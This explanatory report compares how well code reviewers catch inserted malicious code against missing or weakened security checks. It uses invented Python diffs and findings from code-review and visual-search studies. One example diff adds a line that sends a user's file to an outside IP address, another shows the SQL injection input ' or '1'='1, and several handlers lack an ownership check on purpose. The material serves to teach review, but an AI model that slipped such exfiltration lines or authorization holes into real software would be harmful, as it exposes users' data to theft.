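# Missing security checks and inserted malicious code: what code reviewers notice

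## What a diff shows when code is added and when a security check is lost

In code review, other developers read a change to a program before the project adopts it. They look for ordinary mistakes, code that will be hard to maintain, and security holes. Paul, Turzo and Bosu (2021), in *Why Security Defects Go Unnoticed during Code Reviews?*, mention Android and Chromium OS as projects where several colleagues must approve every change, and add that review can also expose attempts to insert malicious code.

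A change can open a security hole by adding harmful code, such as a line that sends customers' files to an outsider. It can also open one by omitting, deleting or loosening a security check, which is code that validates input, confirms that a user may do something, or escapes data before use. Reviewers plausibly catch harmful additions more readily than lost checks. If so, a project that relies on review to catch both is less protected than its maintainers think.

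### What the reviewer sees

On GitHub, a widely used site for hosting code, review takes place in a pull request. GitHub's *About pull requests* defines this as a proposal to merge code changes from one branch into another. A branch is a separate line of work within the project's repository, which stores the project's files and their history. The author gives the pull request a title and usually a description of what the change is for. According to GitHub's *Pull requests*, the page also has a Conversation tab with the description and comments, a Checks tab with the results of automated tests and builds, a Findings tab with alerts from automated scanning, and a Files changed tab with the diff, which shows the change itself.

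GitHub's *Reviewing proposed changes in a pull request* recommends going through the changed files one at a time, commenting on particular lines, and marking each file as viewed, which collapses it and advances a progress bar. The reviewer then comments, approves or requests changes. GitHub also advises reviewers to first read linked issues (the project's records of bugs and requests) to learn why the change was proposed, and to check that the result matches the original intent. A reviewer who wants more than the diff can open the pull request in an online editor and run the code. A request for changes is only advice unless the repository requires approval before merging.

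A diff omits most of the program. It consists of hunks, each showing one area where the old and new versions of a file differ. According to the GNU `diff` manual, lines common to both versions begin with a space, deleted lines with a minus sign and added lines with a plus sign. An edited line normally appears as a deletion followed by an addition. GNU's *Unified Format* and Git's *diff-context-options* (2025) both give a default of three unchanged lines of context around a change. GNU notes that `patch`, a program that applies diffs to files automatically, typically needs at least three lines of context to work properly. That is enough to find the right place in a file, but a reviewer who wants to know who is supposed to reach that code may need much more.

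### Three kinds of security check

Input validation confirms that data from outside has the form and range that the program expects. In a shop's ordering page, written in the programming language Python, it might be a single line:

```python
if not 1 <= quantity <= 100: abort(400)
```

Here `abort` stops the request and returns an error; 400 is the web's code for a malformed request.

Authorization decides whether a particular user may do a particular thing. It differs from authentication, which establishes who the user is, typically by asking for a password. The definition in the Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE), the standard numbered catalogue of software weaknesses, keeps the two apart: in the copy at CVE Find's *CWE-862 Detail*, authorization takes the user's identity as given and determines whether that user can access a given resource. Every customer of a bank can sign in, and none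 of them should see another customer's statement. An authorization check compares the person with the thing:

```python
if doc.owner_id != current_user.id: abort(403)
```

The code 403 means "forbidden".

Escaping rewrites characters that would otherwise act as instructions in the place where the program is about to put them. A site that displays visitors' comments needs something like this:

```python
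page += html.escape(comment)
```

Without the call to `html.escape`, a script in a comment would run in the browser of everyone who opened the page. This flaw is usually called cross-site scripting.

### One handler, four changes

A handler is the function that answers requests for one web address. The handler below, an invented example, returns a document by its number, so a request for `/documents/1042` returns document 1042. Only a document's owner is allowed to read it.

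```python
@app.get("/documents/<int:number>")
@login_required
def show_document(number):
    doc = find_document(number)
    if doc.owner_id != current_user.id:
        abort(403)
    return send_file(doc.path)
```

The top line maps the function to its URL and accepts only whole numbers, a small piece of input validation. `@login_required` blocks anyone who has not signed in. The two lines that begin with `if` are the ownership check.

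Suppose that the handler does not exist yet, and a pull request adds it without those two lines:

```diff
@@ -21,3 +21,9 @@
 @app.get("/about")
 def about():
     return render_template("about.html")
+
+@app.get("/documents/<int:number>")
+@login_required
+def show_document(number):
+    doc = find_document(number)
+    return send_file(doc.path)
```

The line between the at-signs shows that three lines starting at line 21 of the old file became nine lines starting at line 21 of the new one. Every added line does something reasonable, and the handler requires a login. But a customer who changes 1042 to 1043 in the browser's address bar receives somebody else's papers. The new code needs to check that the papers belong to the customer, but that check was never written, so no line of the diff shows that it is missing.

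To object to the missing ownership check, the reviewer must know that documents are private to their owners and that `find_document` does not check ownership itself. Neither fact is in the diff. The same diff would be correct on a site that published free brochures. The privacy rule might be in a linked issue, a policy document, or a similar handler in another file, or it might be known only to people who have worked on the site for years.

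Now suppose that the full handler is already in use, and a pull request deletes the check:

```diff
@@ -26,6 +26,4 @@
 @login_required
 def show_document(number):
     doc = find_document(number)
-    if doc.owner_id != current_user.id:
-        abort(403)
     return send_file(doc.path)
```

This time the diff contains the rule. Even a reviewer who has never seen the site can tell from the deleted lines that the program used to refuse anyone but the owner, and can ask why it should stop. The reviewer still has to find out whether other code now does this check, and whether the team has decided that documents should be open. The reviewer may find the answers in the title and description, but the person who deleted the check also wrote those. With three lines of context, the diff no longer shows the line with the web address, so the function's name is the only clue to what outsiders can request.

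A third pull request keeps the check and loosens it:

```diff
@@ -26,6 +26,6 @@
 @login_required
 def show_document(number):
     doc = find_document(number)
-    if doc.owner_id != current_user.id:
+    if not current_user.is_authenticated:
         abort(403)
     return send_file(doc.path)
```

The handler still has a condition that can return "forbidden", but it now tests whether the visitor has signed in instead of whether the visitor owns the document. This is a weakened check, one that remains but lets more through. Here it has no effect, because `@login_required`, on the first line of the hunk, already turns away everyone the new condition would refuse. To object, the reviewer must compare the meaning of the old and new conditions, know that `is_authenticated` is true of every signed-in user, and know that being signed in is not a sufficient reason to read a document. The deleted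 ownership test is strong evidence for the last point, if the reviewer reads it.

The fourth change leaves the ownership check alone and adds a line beneath it:

```diff
@@ -28,4 +28,5 @@
     doc = find_document(number)
     if doc.owner_id != current_user.id:
         abort(403)
+    socket.create_connection(("203.0.113.9", 443)).sendall(open(doc.path, "rb").read())
     return send_file(doc.path)
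```

Whenever an owner opens a document, the new line connects to a machine at a numeric address and sends it the whole file. This is inserted malicious code, meaning added code whose own action is harmful. To spot it, a reviewer needs to know some Python but nothing about the site. The bare address, the outgoing connection and the reading of the entire file are each a visible cue, something a reader can recognise as dangerous from the displayed lines alone. If the file did not already import Python's `socket` library, the diff would also show an added import line, which would be another cue. The address might belong to the company's own backup server, but the displayed lines are enough to justify stopping the change and asking. Real attackers can disguise such a line far better.

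In these examples, the reviewer needs outside knowledge most for the never-written check and least for the inserted line. The deleted and weakened checks fall between them, because the diff shows the old rule but the reviewer must still judge whether removing it was right. Paul and colleagues make a related distinction between flaws that a reviewer can identify from a few lines of code and flaws that require running the program or understanding much more of it. Their categories do not separate added code from deleted code, so they match the four versions only loosely. Studies also find that reviewers detect some kinds of flaw much more often than others.

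That study's method also shows why a check that was never written is hard to trace. The researchers wanted to trace known vulnerabilities in Chromium OS back to the changes that had introduced them. Where a later fix had altered or deleted a line, they could use Git's `blame` command, which identifies the change that last touched each line. Where a fix had only inserted lines, the old file had no faulty line to trace. They therefore ran `blame` on the lines just before and after the insertion, reasoning that security fixes often add checks right before an access or after a function call, and then inspected the results by hand.

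### Where text, effect and intent come apart

Plus and minus signs record changes to text. They are a poor guide to whether a program has become more or less protected. The following change deletes nothing:

```diff
@@ -26,6 +26,8 @@
 @login_required
 def show_document(number):
     doc = find_document(number)
+    if request.args.get("preview"):
+        return send_file(doc.path)
     if doc.owner_id != current_user.id:
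         abort(403)
     return send_file(doc.path)
```

Any signed-in user who adds `?preview=1` to the address now gets the file before the program reaches the ownership check. The diff still shows the whole check as unchanged context. The reviewer has to follow the order in which the lines run to see the hole, and the added lines look like a small convenience feature.

Deleting a security check can be harmless. A developer may remove the ownership check from `show_document` because `find_document` now performs it for every handler on the site. This is often an improvement, because developers can't then forget the check when they write a new handler. If the same pull request changes `find_document`, the reviewer can find the new check in another hunk, perhaps in another file. If an earlier pull request made that change, the diff shows only the two deleted lines, exactly as it would if the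 check had been lost. A reviewer who objected to every deleted check would therefore raise some false alarms, but would sooner or later approve a real hole by accepting "moved elsewhere" without looking.

A diff does not show intent either. The handler without an ownership check could come from a developer in a hurry, from one who believed the documents were public, or from someone who wanted a way in and knew the omission would look like an oversight. Even the line that sends files to a numeric address might be left over from testing. This report therefore uses the term "inserted malicious code" based on what the code does, whatever its author intended. Reviewers can refuse a change without knowing the author's motive, but motive still matters for the comparison because someone who means harm can choose the form of the change, and leaving out a check gives them access that they can explain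 as a mistake.

### How missing authorization ranks

Flaws like the one in the example are common in released software. MITRE, the US non-profit that operates CWE, ranks weaknesses every year, and its *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025), the latest edition, puts Missing Authorization (CWE-862) fourth, up from ninth the year before. GCVE's copy of the CWE entry, *CWE 862*, describes a product that performs no authorization check when someone tries to access a resource or perform an action. This description applies whether a new handler never had the check or an edit deleted it, because CWE classifies flaws by what is wrong with the program, however they were introduced.

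Several other entries on the list are relevant to the same example. Incorrect Authorization, the closest match for the weakened check, is 17th. Authorization Bypass Through User-Controlled Key is 24th, up from 30th. It describes the document site almost exactly, since the "key" is the number in the address that a visitor can edit. Missing Authentication for Critical Function is 21st and Improper Input Validation is 18th. Cross-site scripting, the usual result of missing escaping, is first, as it was a year earlier.

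The other well-known ranking comes from the Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a community that publishes guidance on web application security. Its list ranks broad categories and has no separate entry for missing authorization, which belongs to Broken Access Control. MITRE's *OWASP Top Ten 2025 Category A01:2025* lists that category as A01, the top entry. WSO2's *OWASP Top 10*, a software vendor's guide to the same list, ranks Injection fifth and Authentication Failures seventh.

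According to MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Key Insights* (2025), the Top 25 is based on 39,080 vulnerability records and ranks weaknesses by severity and prevalence. Ranking them by confirmed attacks gives a different order. By MITRE's count, the US government's catalogue of vulnerabilities known to have been exploited includes no records for Missing Authorization, 11 for Missing Authentication for Critical Function, and 20 for operating-system command injection. These rankings are only indirect evidence about reviewers, because they count flaws that reached finished products, some of which may never have gone through review, and they don't distinguish checks that were never written from checks that were deleted.

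## What studies of reviewers found about visible flaws and missing checks

The studies described below examined questions such as which types of security flaw reviewers tend to miss, and whether people who read code notice that something is absent. The results are fairly direct evidence about missing checks and very indirect evidence about inserted malicious code. None of the studies tested the claim directly by giving the same reviewers two sets of similar pull requests, one with inserted malicious code and one with missing checks, and counting how many of each they caught.

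### Caught and missed flaws in Chromium OS

Paul and colleagues drew on 404,878 review requests in the Chromium OS project from March 2011 to March 2019. They used different methods to collect reviews that had caught a security flaw and reviews that had missed one.

To find reviews that had caught a vulnerability, the researchers searched the review comments for 105 security-related words, such as "overflow", "race", "permission" and "leak". Two of them went through the 7,572 matching comments and discarded those that clearly raised no security concern, which left 1,337 to examine together with the code. They counted a review only if the reviewer had pointed to a possible vulnerability, they agreed after their own analysis, and the code's author had either admitted the mistake or made the recommended change. In total, 516 reviews met these criteria.

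The missed bugs came from the project's bug tracker. Of 591 security bugs marked as fixed, 239 had fixes that went through the project's review system. The researchers traced those fixes back to 374 earlier changes that had helped introduce the bugs, and to the reviews that had approved them.

The researchers gave each flaw a CWE type and merged the 86 types that occurred into 15 broader ones. The table shows seven of these.

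| Type of flaw | CWE number | Reviews that caught it | Reviews that missed it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Use of a potentially dangerous function | 676 | 53 | 0 |
| Improper resource shutdown or release | 404 | 71 | 4 |
| Improper input validation | 20 | 9 | 72 |
| Improper access control | 284 | 8 | 58 |
| Insufficient verification of data authenticity | 345 | 0 | 13 |
| Use of a resource after its expiration or release | 672 | 3 | 62 |
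| Incorrect type conversion | 704 | 1 | 16 |

A typical dangerous function is C's `strcpy`, which copies text without checking that the destination has room for it. A reviewer who knows the name can object without further information. The flaw types closest to a missing or inadequate security check are input validation, access control and data authenticity. A program has an authenticity flaw when it accepts data without confirming where they came from or that nobody has altered them. In the sample, reviewers caught 17 flaws of these three types and missed 143.

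The share of input-validation flaws that Chromium OS reviewers catch can't be calculated from the 9 caught and 72 missed. The two counts come from separate searches, and nobody knows what share of all catches or all misses each search found. Taken at face value, they give a catch rate of 11%. If the keyword search found only a quarter of the relevant comments, reviewers would have caught 36 such flaws, and with 72 misses the rate would be 33%. If the search found every catch but half of the missed flaws are still undiscovered, the rate would be about 6%. The overall ratio of 516 to 374 has the same problem, since it reflects how many cases the researchers were able to collect.

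A study of this design can compare types of flaw. In the sample, reviewers caught almost 18 unreleased resources for each one they missed, but they missed eight input-validation flaws for each one they caught. The odds of a catch are 142 times as high for unreleased resources as for input-validation flaws. This ratio would be the same if the keyword search had overlooked three quarters of all catches, as long as it overlooked the same share for every type.

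The comparison fails only if the searches favoured some types over others, and they probably did to some extent. The comment "this leaks memory" matches the word list, but "who checks that the caller owns this file?" contains none of the 105 words. Paul and colleagues argue that such omissions do not affect their study, because they considered only reviews that they had confirmed as catches. That supports the individual entries but not the comparison between types. The bug tracker is also biased, because it lists only flaws that somebody later recognised as security bugs. A stray `strcpy` that no attacker can reach may never be listed, and one that is listed may appear under its consequence, as a memory-buffer error (42 caught, 16 missed). This may partly explain the zero in the top row. Still, the searches would have to be extremely lopsided to produce a 142-fold gap by themselves. The ordering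 of the types is probably real, but the exact size of the gap is not reliable.

The table shows that reviewers in this sample caught some flaws caused by missing code and overlooked others that were visible in the code. They nearly always caught unreleased resources, where a program opens a file or reserves memory but lacks the line that should give it back. They also did well on improper synchronization (109 caught, 13 missed), which often involves a missing lock around data that several threads share. But they missed nearly all the incorrect type conversions and cases in which a program uses a resource after releasing it, even though the faulty line is present in the code.

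Paul and colleagues distinguish flaws that show in a few lines from flaws that take more to recognise, and that distinction fits these rows better. A reviewer who sees a line that opens a file knows to look for a line that closes it, usually nearby. No line in the document handler prompts the reviewer to look for an ownership check. Recognising an invalid use of released memory requires knowing about the code elsewhere that released it. On this evidence, reviewers have trouble with omissions mainly when the displayed code gives no sign that something should be there.

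The study is weakest on inserted malicious code. Its word list included "backdoor", "trojan" and "malware", but none of the 15 types covers deliberately harmful code. Dangerous functions come closest, because a reviewer can recognise them on sight, but a developer who writes `strcpy` out of habit is not trying to hide it, as an attacker might.

### Changes that touch many directories

Paul and colleagues also looked for features of a review that were associated with catching or missing a flaw. They used logistic regression, which estimates how each of several factors changes the odds of an outcome. The strongest factor was the number of directories (folders of the project's files) that the change touched, which ranged from one to ten. Its odds ratio was 0.76, which the researchers interpret to mean that each additional directory multiplies the odds of a catch by 0.76. On that reading, a change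 across four directories would have less than half the odds of a change in one. The model allowed this effect to vary with the number of directories, so 0.76 is best taken as a summary.

The effects of a change's size and spread are hard to separate here, because the numbers of directories, files and changed lines were so closely correlated that the researchers kept only directories in the model. A reviewer may miss more in a scattered change because the parts are hard to connect, or simply because there is more to read. The researchers also did not estimate the effect for each type of flaw, so the figure is not specific to missing checks. It still suggests an added risk in moving an ownership check out of many handlers into one shared function, since such a change may touch several directories.

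The number of reviewers made no significant difference to whether a flaw was caught. Reviewers who had done more reviews were slightly less likely to catch one. The researchers suggest this may come from fatigue or haste, although these reviewers may also receive harder changes. The odds of catching a flaw were 4.55 times as high when the change fixed an existing bug, and the researchers think reviewers take more care with such changes. They also cite work by Munaiah and colleagues on the related Chromium project, where reviews with less inquisitive discussion were more likely to have missed a vulnerability. All of these are correlations in the records of two related projects.

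### Two missing checks, one with a familiar attack

In an experiment, researchers know exactly which flaw each reviewer was shown. For *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?*, Braz, Fregnan and colleagues (2021) recruited participants through web forums, social media and their own contacts, without revealing that the study was about security. After exclusions, 146 participants remained, and 105 of them reported at least three years of professional development experience. Each participant reviewed a change to a program that manages employees' holidays, written in Java and about 140 lines long. The old and new code appeared side by side in an interface modelled on Gerrit, the review tool that Chromium OS uses.

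The researchers assigned each participant at random to one of two versions. Both accepted input from a user without validating it. Simplified and put into Python, the two faulty lines look like this:

```python
query = "SELECT * FROM employees WHERE id = '" + employee_id + "'"
cost = days_to_buy * price_multiplier(level) * 10
```

The `query` line pastes the user's text straight into a database command. Someone who types `' or '1'='1` as an employee number changes the command so that it matches every employee. This flaw, called SQL injection, has been a textbook example for years. The `cost` line calculates what an employee pays for extra days of holiday. The program doesn't check for negative numbers, so if an employee asks for minus five days, the cost is negative and the program credits the employee with money.

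Both flaws are missing checks, and in both versions the displayed code was enough to find the flaw and work out how to exploit it. The versions differed in their visible cues. Many developers have learned to distrust text joined to a database command with plus signs, but the multiplication in the other version looks ordinary.

The researchers also planted an ordinary bug in both versions to check that participants were making an effort. After the first review, they told everyone that the change contained a vulnerability, without saying what kind, and asked those who had missed it to look again.

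| | SQL injection | Missing check for negative numbers |
|---|---|---|
| Found the ordinary bug | 39 of 80 (49%) | 37 of 66 (56%) |
| Found the flaw in the first review | 52 of 80 (65%) | 14 of 66 (21%) |
| Found it after the warning, among those who had missed it | 13 of 28 (46%) | 7 of 52 (13%) |
| Found it in either review | 65 of 80 (81%) | 21 of 66 (32%) |

The percentages here are calculated from the counts. For the missing check, the paper's text gives 18% for the first review and 40% for the two reviews together, but neither figure matches the paper's tables.

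The two groups did about equally well on the ordinary bug, so a difference in effort or skill is unlikely to explain the gap on the security flaws. Braz and colleagues estimated that the odds of finding the SQL injection were about seven times those of finding the missing check for negative numbers (95% confidence interval 3.3 to 14.6). The gap remained in a regression that accounted for experience, training and working habits. In that regression, participants who said they reviewed code often were also more likely to find the flaw, as were those who said they thought about vulnerabilities while writing code.

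Because validation was missing from both versions, this experiment does not compare an omission with an insertion, but it isolates the effect of a visible cue better than the Chromium OS records can. Reviewers in those records mostly missed improper input validation, whereas almost two thirds of participants here found an example of it in a single reading when the faulty line looked like a known attack. A recognisable cue would presumably make inserted malicious code easier to notice too, but that is an inference, because no participant saw any such code.

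The experiment does not show how much of the advantage comes from how the line looks and how much from how well known the attack is. Participants who found the SQL injection at once most often said that it is common and easy to notice, that they had met it before, and that they knew about it. Those who found the missing check for negative numbers more often credited a habit, such as always looking at what a user can supply. Braz and colleagues expect the result to carry over to other vulnerabilities only where a similarly popular attack exists. The experiment used only one example of each kind of flaw, so some other difference between the two may also have played a part.

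### What the warning changed

Security seldom comes up in ordinary code review. *A Security Perspective on Code Review* (2016), by di Biase, Bruntink and Bacchelli, examined 114 security issues that Chromium project reviews had identified and 71 they had missed. Braz and colleagues cite it for the finding that only about 1% of the project's review comments concerned potential security flaws. In their own study, they gave reviewers a warning to find out how much of the problem goes away when reviewers know there is something to look for.

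The reminder to focus on security helped participants who reviewed the SQL injection far more than those who reviewed the code with no check for negative numbers. Nearly half of the people who had missed the injection then found it, and 13 said they had needed the reminder. A few said they had noticed the problem earlier but had not been sure of it. Of the 52 who had not noticed the missing check, 45 missed it again. Their reasons included inattention, a focus on other aspects of the code and a lack of knowledge. Eight had mistaken the planted ordinary bug for the vulnerability. Across both versions, 60 of the 146 participants never found the flaw.

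Everyone who had missed the flaw received the warning, so the experiment had no group that looked again without one. Some of the 20 late finds may be due more to the second look than to the warning. This makes the result for the negative numbers more discouraging, because a warning and a second reading together helped only about one in eight reviewers. Researchers tested more specific instructions and checklists in 2022.

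The experiment differed from everyday review in ways that could have raised or lowered the detection rate. Participants reviewed a stranger's program with nothing at stake, and people may look harder at their own project, whose rules they would also know. But the change was short and self-contained, while real pull requests can be much larger. Reviewers also needed no outside information to see that minus five days of holiday is absurd. Reviewers who do not know the document site would probably notice its missing ownership check at a lower rate than the 21% in this experiment.

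Reviewers still miss security flaws when they are told from the start to look for them. Braz and colleagues cite an earlier experiment on security-focused manual review and describe the effectiveness it measured as relatively low. In that experiment, 30 hired developers examined a small web application with seven known vulnerabilities, and none of them found all seven. More experienced reviewers were not necessarily more accurate, and people who reported more real flaws also tended to report more false ones. The vulnerabilities were cross-site scripting, SQL injection and cross-site request forgery, in which a hostile page makes a signed-in user's browser send a request the user never intended. Applications usually prevent cross-site request forgery by checking for a secret token that only their own pages can supply. All three types result from missing protection, and the experiment included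 no inserted malicious code to compare them with.

### Omissions when readers have a specification

Researchers on software testing have long distinguished faults of omission from faults of commission. In *Comparing the Effectiveness of Software Testing Strategies* (1985, published in a journal in 1987), Basili and Selby define a fault of omission as one that results from a programmer forgetting to include something, such as a statement that gives a variable its proper value. A fault of commission is an incorrect piece of existing code, such as a plus sign where a minus sign belongs. The faults were ordinary mistakes, so the distinction has nothing to do with malice.

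Their 74 subjects were 42 advanced students at the University of Maryland and 32 professional programmers from NASA and a contractor. They looked for 34 faults in four small programs, and each person used three techniques on three different programs.

In code reading, the person received the source code and a specification of what the program should do. They worked out what each small part did, combined these findings into a description of the whole program, and compared it with the specification. In functional testing, the person had the specification and could run the program but did not see its code. In structural testing, the person read the code and chose inputs until every statement had run at least once, and received the specification only afterwards, to judge the output.

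Code readers and functional testers both found more faults of omission than structural testers did, and did not differ significantly from each other. Of the structural testers, 44% found no omission faults in the program they tested. Basili and Selby had expected structural testing to do badly. A tester who aims to run every statement has no reason to choose an input that would expose a missing one.

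Among the professionals, code readers also found the most faults overall, averaging 1.24 more per program than those who used functional or structural testing, although the source code had no comments. In one group of students, reading and functional testing did equally well and structural testing did worse, and in the other group the techniques did not differ. Readers were the best at finding interface faults, which arise when one part of a program makes a wrong assumption about another part. A missing security check is often a fault of this kind. In the document example, a developer might leave out the ownership check because they believe `find_document` already performs it.

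These results suggest that people can find missing code by reading. They do not show that missing code is as easy to find as wrong code, because the result for omissions ranks the three techniques and does not compare how well code readers found each kind of fault. The programs were also complete and at most a few hundred lines long, so readers saw all the code, and very few of the omissions were probably missing security checks.

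Later experiments are less favourable to reading. In *Towards a Framework to Compare Formal Experiments that Evaluate Testing Techniques*, Vallespir, Moreno and colleagues compare Basili and Selby's study with several successors. Kamsties and Lott (1995) used 50 students and concluded that the techniques can be equally effective for people without much experience if time does not matter. In a first experiment with 196 students, Juristo and Vegas found that success depended on the program and the particular fault as well as on the technique. In their second experiment, with 46 students, code reading did worse than both kinds of testing, whatever the type of fault. Experience may explain part of the disagreement, because the successors used students, while Basili and Selby also had professionals, and code reading did best among the professionals. Vallespir and colleagues also note that the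 researchers had planted most of the faults themselves, which they consider less realistic than industrial practice.

Taken together, the testing experiments leave it uncertain whether careful reading is a good way to find omissions. It did well in the version that gave the reader a specification, which pull requests often lack. If the document site's specification included the rule "only the owner may read a document", a reader who worked out that the faulty handler "returns any document to any signed-in user" would find that the two don't match. In a pull request, the nearest thing to a specification is often the author's own description, and an author who forgot the ownership check may have left the rule out of the description for the same reason.

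## Why a check that was never written is hard to notice

Without a specification, reviewers have to remember the rule themselves, and when a check was never written, they also have to notice that it is missing.

### What the reviewer has to work out

Consider again the new document handler, which requires a login but never compares the document's owner with the user. Before reviewers can say with confidence that it is insecure, they have to:

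- recall that a rule applies
- know where the program normally enforces it
- establish that no other part of the program enforces it here
- judge that an attacker can reach the code.

The example shows how each of these steps can fail. The studies of Chromium OS and of the flaw with negative numbers did not measure the steps separately, so they don't show how often each one fails.

To notice a missing check, a reviewer has to recall the rule it would enforce. A reviewer who joined the project last month may never have learned that documents are private. Others may know it well but not think of it while reading a few lines that fetch a file. Such lapses seem to be common. In PortSwigger's *The road to DevSecOps isn’t always the smoothest*, Alberto Bacchelli, who co-wrote *A Security Perspective on Code Review*, says that developers in his group's earlier studies often missed vulnerabilities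 they may have known how to detect.

To notice a missing ownership check, a reviewer needs to know where the program enforces ownership. A site can do this in each handler, in the shared function that finds documents, in a layer that processes every request before any handler runs, or in the database. A reviewer who is used to projects where the shared function checks ownership will think the new handler is complete. The line `@login_required` can also look like sufficient access control.

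A reviewer looking for an ownership check can stop if `find_document` compares the document's owner with the user. But to conclude that the check is missing, the reviewer has to look everywhere it could be, and all of those places may be outside the diff. It is quicker to assume that another layer handles the check.

The reviewer must judge whether an attacker can reach the code. This is easy for the document handler, because its first line gives a web address. It is harder when the new code is a function deep inside the program, because the reviewer may believe that only staff can trigger it or that an earlier function has already validated the data. The reviewer must also imagine somebody supplying the harmful input, such as an employee asking the holiday program to buy minus five days.

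Before completing all this, reviewers can ask the author, "What stops another customer from opening this?" To ask, they only need to remember the rule. The author then does the remaining work, and may still get it wrong. Forgetting the rule is therefore the most damaging failure, because then nobody asks. By contrast, a line that sends customers' files to an unknown address can prompt a question by itself.

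### Three explanations and what they predict

There are at least three plausible reasons why reviewers miss never-written checks.

People may be poor at noticing missing things of any kind. If so, reviewers should do badly on every kind of omission, even when the displayed code contains everything they need to spot it.

Another explanation may be that a missing check usually leaves no visible cue. If so, we would expect reviewers to catch an omission when the displayed code contains a clue to it, such as a line that leads the reader to expect another. We would also expect them to miss badly written code that looks ordinary.

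Reviewers may also miss the problem because the evidence they need is outside the diff, either in another file or in knowledge nobody wrote down. If so, they should do well when the diff shows everything they need, and people who know the project should do better than strangers.

Two results from the previous section allow a rough test.

| Explanation | Unreleased resource | Missing check for negative numbers |
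|---|---|---|
| Absence is hard to perceive | Reviewers miss it | Reviewers miss it |
| The flaw lacks a visible cue | Reviewers catch it, because the line that opens the resource prompts them to look for the line that closes it | Reviewers miss it, because the calculation looks ordinary |
| The deciding evidence is outside the diff | Reviewers catch it if the closing line belongs nearby | Reviewers catch it, because everything they need is on the screen |
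| **What happened** | **Mostly caught** | **Mostly missed** |

Only the lack of a visible cue fits both results. Participants in the holiday experiment found the SQL injection more readily than the missing check for negative numbers. Both programs lacked validation, so the difficulty of noticing something absent cannot explain this difference either.

If a cue is simply whatever reviewers notice, the explanation based on cues can never be proven wrong. SQL injection is a reasonable test of it, since textbooks warned about SQL injection long before the experiment. Unreleased resources are a weaker test, because the idea that the line that opens a resource works as a cue is an interpretation of counts that were already known.

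Correia, Pinto-Albuquerque and colleagues (2024) found a similar pattern in a small study of specialists. In *Improving Industrial Cybersecurity Training*, they asked 12 industrial security professionals to find the vulnerability in each of five C++ snippets. All 12 found the SQL injection and 10 found the cross-site scripting, which the researchers attribute to how well known those flaws are. Six found a buffer overflow, where a program writes more data into an area of memory than it can hold, and five found improper input validation. Only two found an out-of-bounds write, a memory error closely related to buffer overflow, although the researchers had ranked that snippet the least complex to analyse. SQL injection and cross-site scripting both come from missing protection, so these professionals had no general difficulty with omissions. But the study used only one snippet for each type of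 flaw, so some other feature of the code could explain the differences.

The evidence on unreleased memory is more mixed than the Chromium OS counts suggest. In *Human Attention During Localization of Memory Bugs in C Programs*, Smith, Wallace and colleagues (2025) gave 21 programmers, most of them students, bug reports for three large programs and asked them to find the cause by reading the code. The researchers scored each answer about the bug's location from 1 to 5, with 0 for no answer. Three of the bugs were leaks, where the program never releases some memory, and their mean scores were 3.20, 1.86 and 1.71. Three others were double frees, where the program releases the same memory twice, and their mean scores were 4.78, 3.44 and 3.13.

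Participants therefore tended to do worse when a release was missing than when there was one too many, which could mean that absence does matter. But in the leak with the highest score, the program reserved the memory in one file and should have released it from another, so neither file alone showed the whole problem. This fits the explanation based on outside evidence. The study also had only eight bugs, which differed in difficulty, and the participants knew from the report that a bug existed, which reviewers usually do not.

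Other evidence suggests that scattered information makes flaws harder to find. *A Systematic Literature Review and Taxonomy of Modern Code Review* (2021) describes research that found a correlation between reviewers' working memory capacity and their effectiveness at finding delocalized defects, which a reader can recognise only by combining several separate pieces of code. The Chromium OS reviewers were also less likely to catch flaws in changes that touched many directories. Both explanations can apply to the same missing check, which may lack a cue and also depend on a rule that is somewhere else, as in the document handler.

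### Searching for something that is not there

Psychologists have found that people have difficulty noticing when something is absent from a simple picture, although this does not explain the results for code. In *Search Asymmetry*, Treisman and Souther (1985) showed eight students cards with 1, 6 or 12 circles. In one condition, the students looked for a circle with a short vertical line through its base among plain circles. In the other, they looked for a plain circle among circles that all had the line. Half the cards contained the target, and the students pressed one of two keys to report whether they saw it.

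Each additional circle on the card added about 4 milliseconds to the time students needed to find the target when it had the line, and 19.7 milliseconds when it was the plain circle. Students missed the plain circle on 13.9% of the 12-circle cards that contained it, while all other error rates were below 4%.

Treisman and Souther's explanation is that early vision registers a simple feature, such as the line, across the whole display at once. When only the target has a line, viewers can answer as soon as they detect one anywhere. When every circle except the target has a line, detecting one doesn't help, so viewers must check the circles one at a time. The times for cards without a target support this. When there was no plain circle to find, each additional circle added 38.9 milliseconds, about twice as much as when there was one. Someone checking one by one finds a target about halfway through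 on average, but must check every circle to be sure there is none.

The presence of a feature is also easier to learn from than its absence. In experiments published in 1969 and 1970, Jenkins and Sainsbury trained pigeons with a lighted key that sometimes carried a black dot. One group saw the dot only on rewarded trials, and the other saw it only on unrewarded trials. The first group learned to tell the trials apart much better. Psychologists call this the feature-positive effect, and Newman, Wolff and Hearst (1980) later reported it in adult humans. If it applies to code, developers should learn to recognize the danger in a call to `strcpy` more easily than in a handler that lacks an ownership check. That would help explain why developers come to recognize some warning signs and never learn others, but these experiments did not involve code.

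The work on circles may carry over only partly to code review. The students knew what they were looking for, and every card showed all the circles. A reviewer does not know in advance which check might be missing, and the diff may show one handler without the twenty others that would make it look odd. On a card of 12 circles, the slower search also took the students less than a fifth of a second longer than the faster one, a trivial delay for somebody who spends ten minutes on a pull request.

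An ownership check also differs from a line through a circle because it consists of ordinary letters and symbols, which readers have to understand before they can recognise the check. Even for simple pictures, Wolfe and Utochkin (2018) note in *What is a preattentive feature?* that no simple test infallibly identifies the features that guide attention in this way. The logic of the comparison still applies, though. Finding one ownership check anywhere proves that the program has one, but a reviewer can prove that there is none only by looking in every place where it might be. Searching for other layers of enforcement therefore takes a lot of effort, regardless of how visual attention works.

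### Flaws that seldom appear

Security flaws are rare in the changes that most reviewers read, and rarity alone makes people miss things. *Rare targets are often missed in visual search* (Wolfe, Horowitz and Kenner, 2005) studied searches similar to those of airport baggage screeners. Participants in that study missed 7% of targets when half the displays contained one, and 30% when only one display in a hundred did, according to *Rare Targets Are Rarely Missed in Correctable Search* (Fleck and Mitroff).

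Fleck and Mitroff then ran their own version with 20 young adults, who looked for a tool among pictures of toys, clothes, fruit and birds. Half the participants could press a key to correct their previous answer.

| Share of displays with a tool | Missed, no correction allowed | Missed, correction allowed |
|---|---|---|
| 50% | 10% | 4% |
| 10% | 19% | 10% |
| 2% | 31% | 10% |

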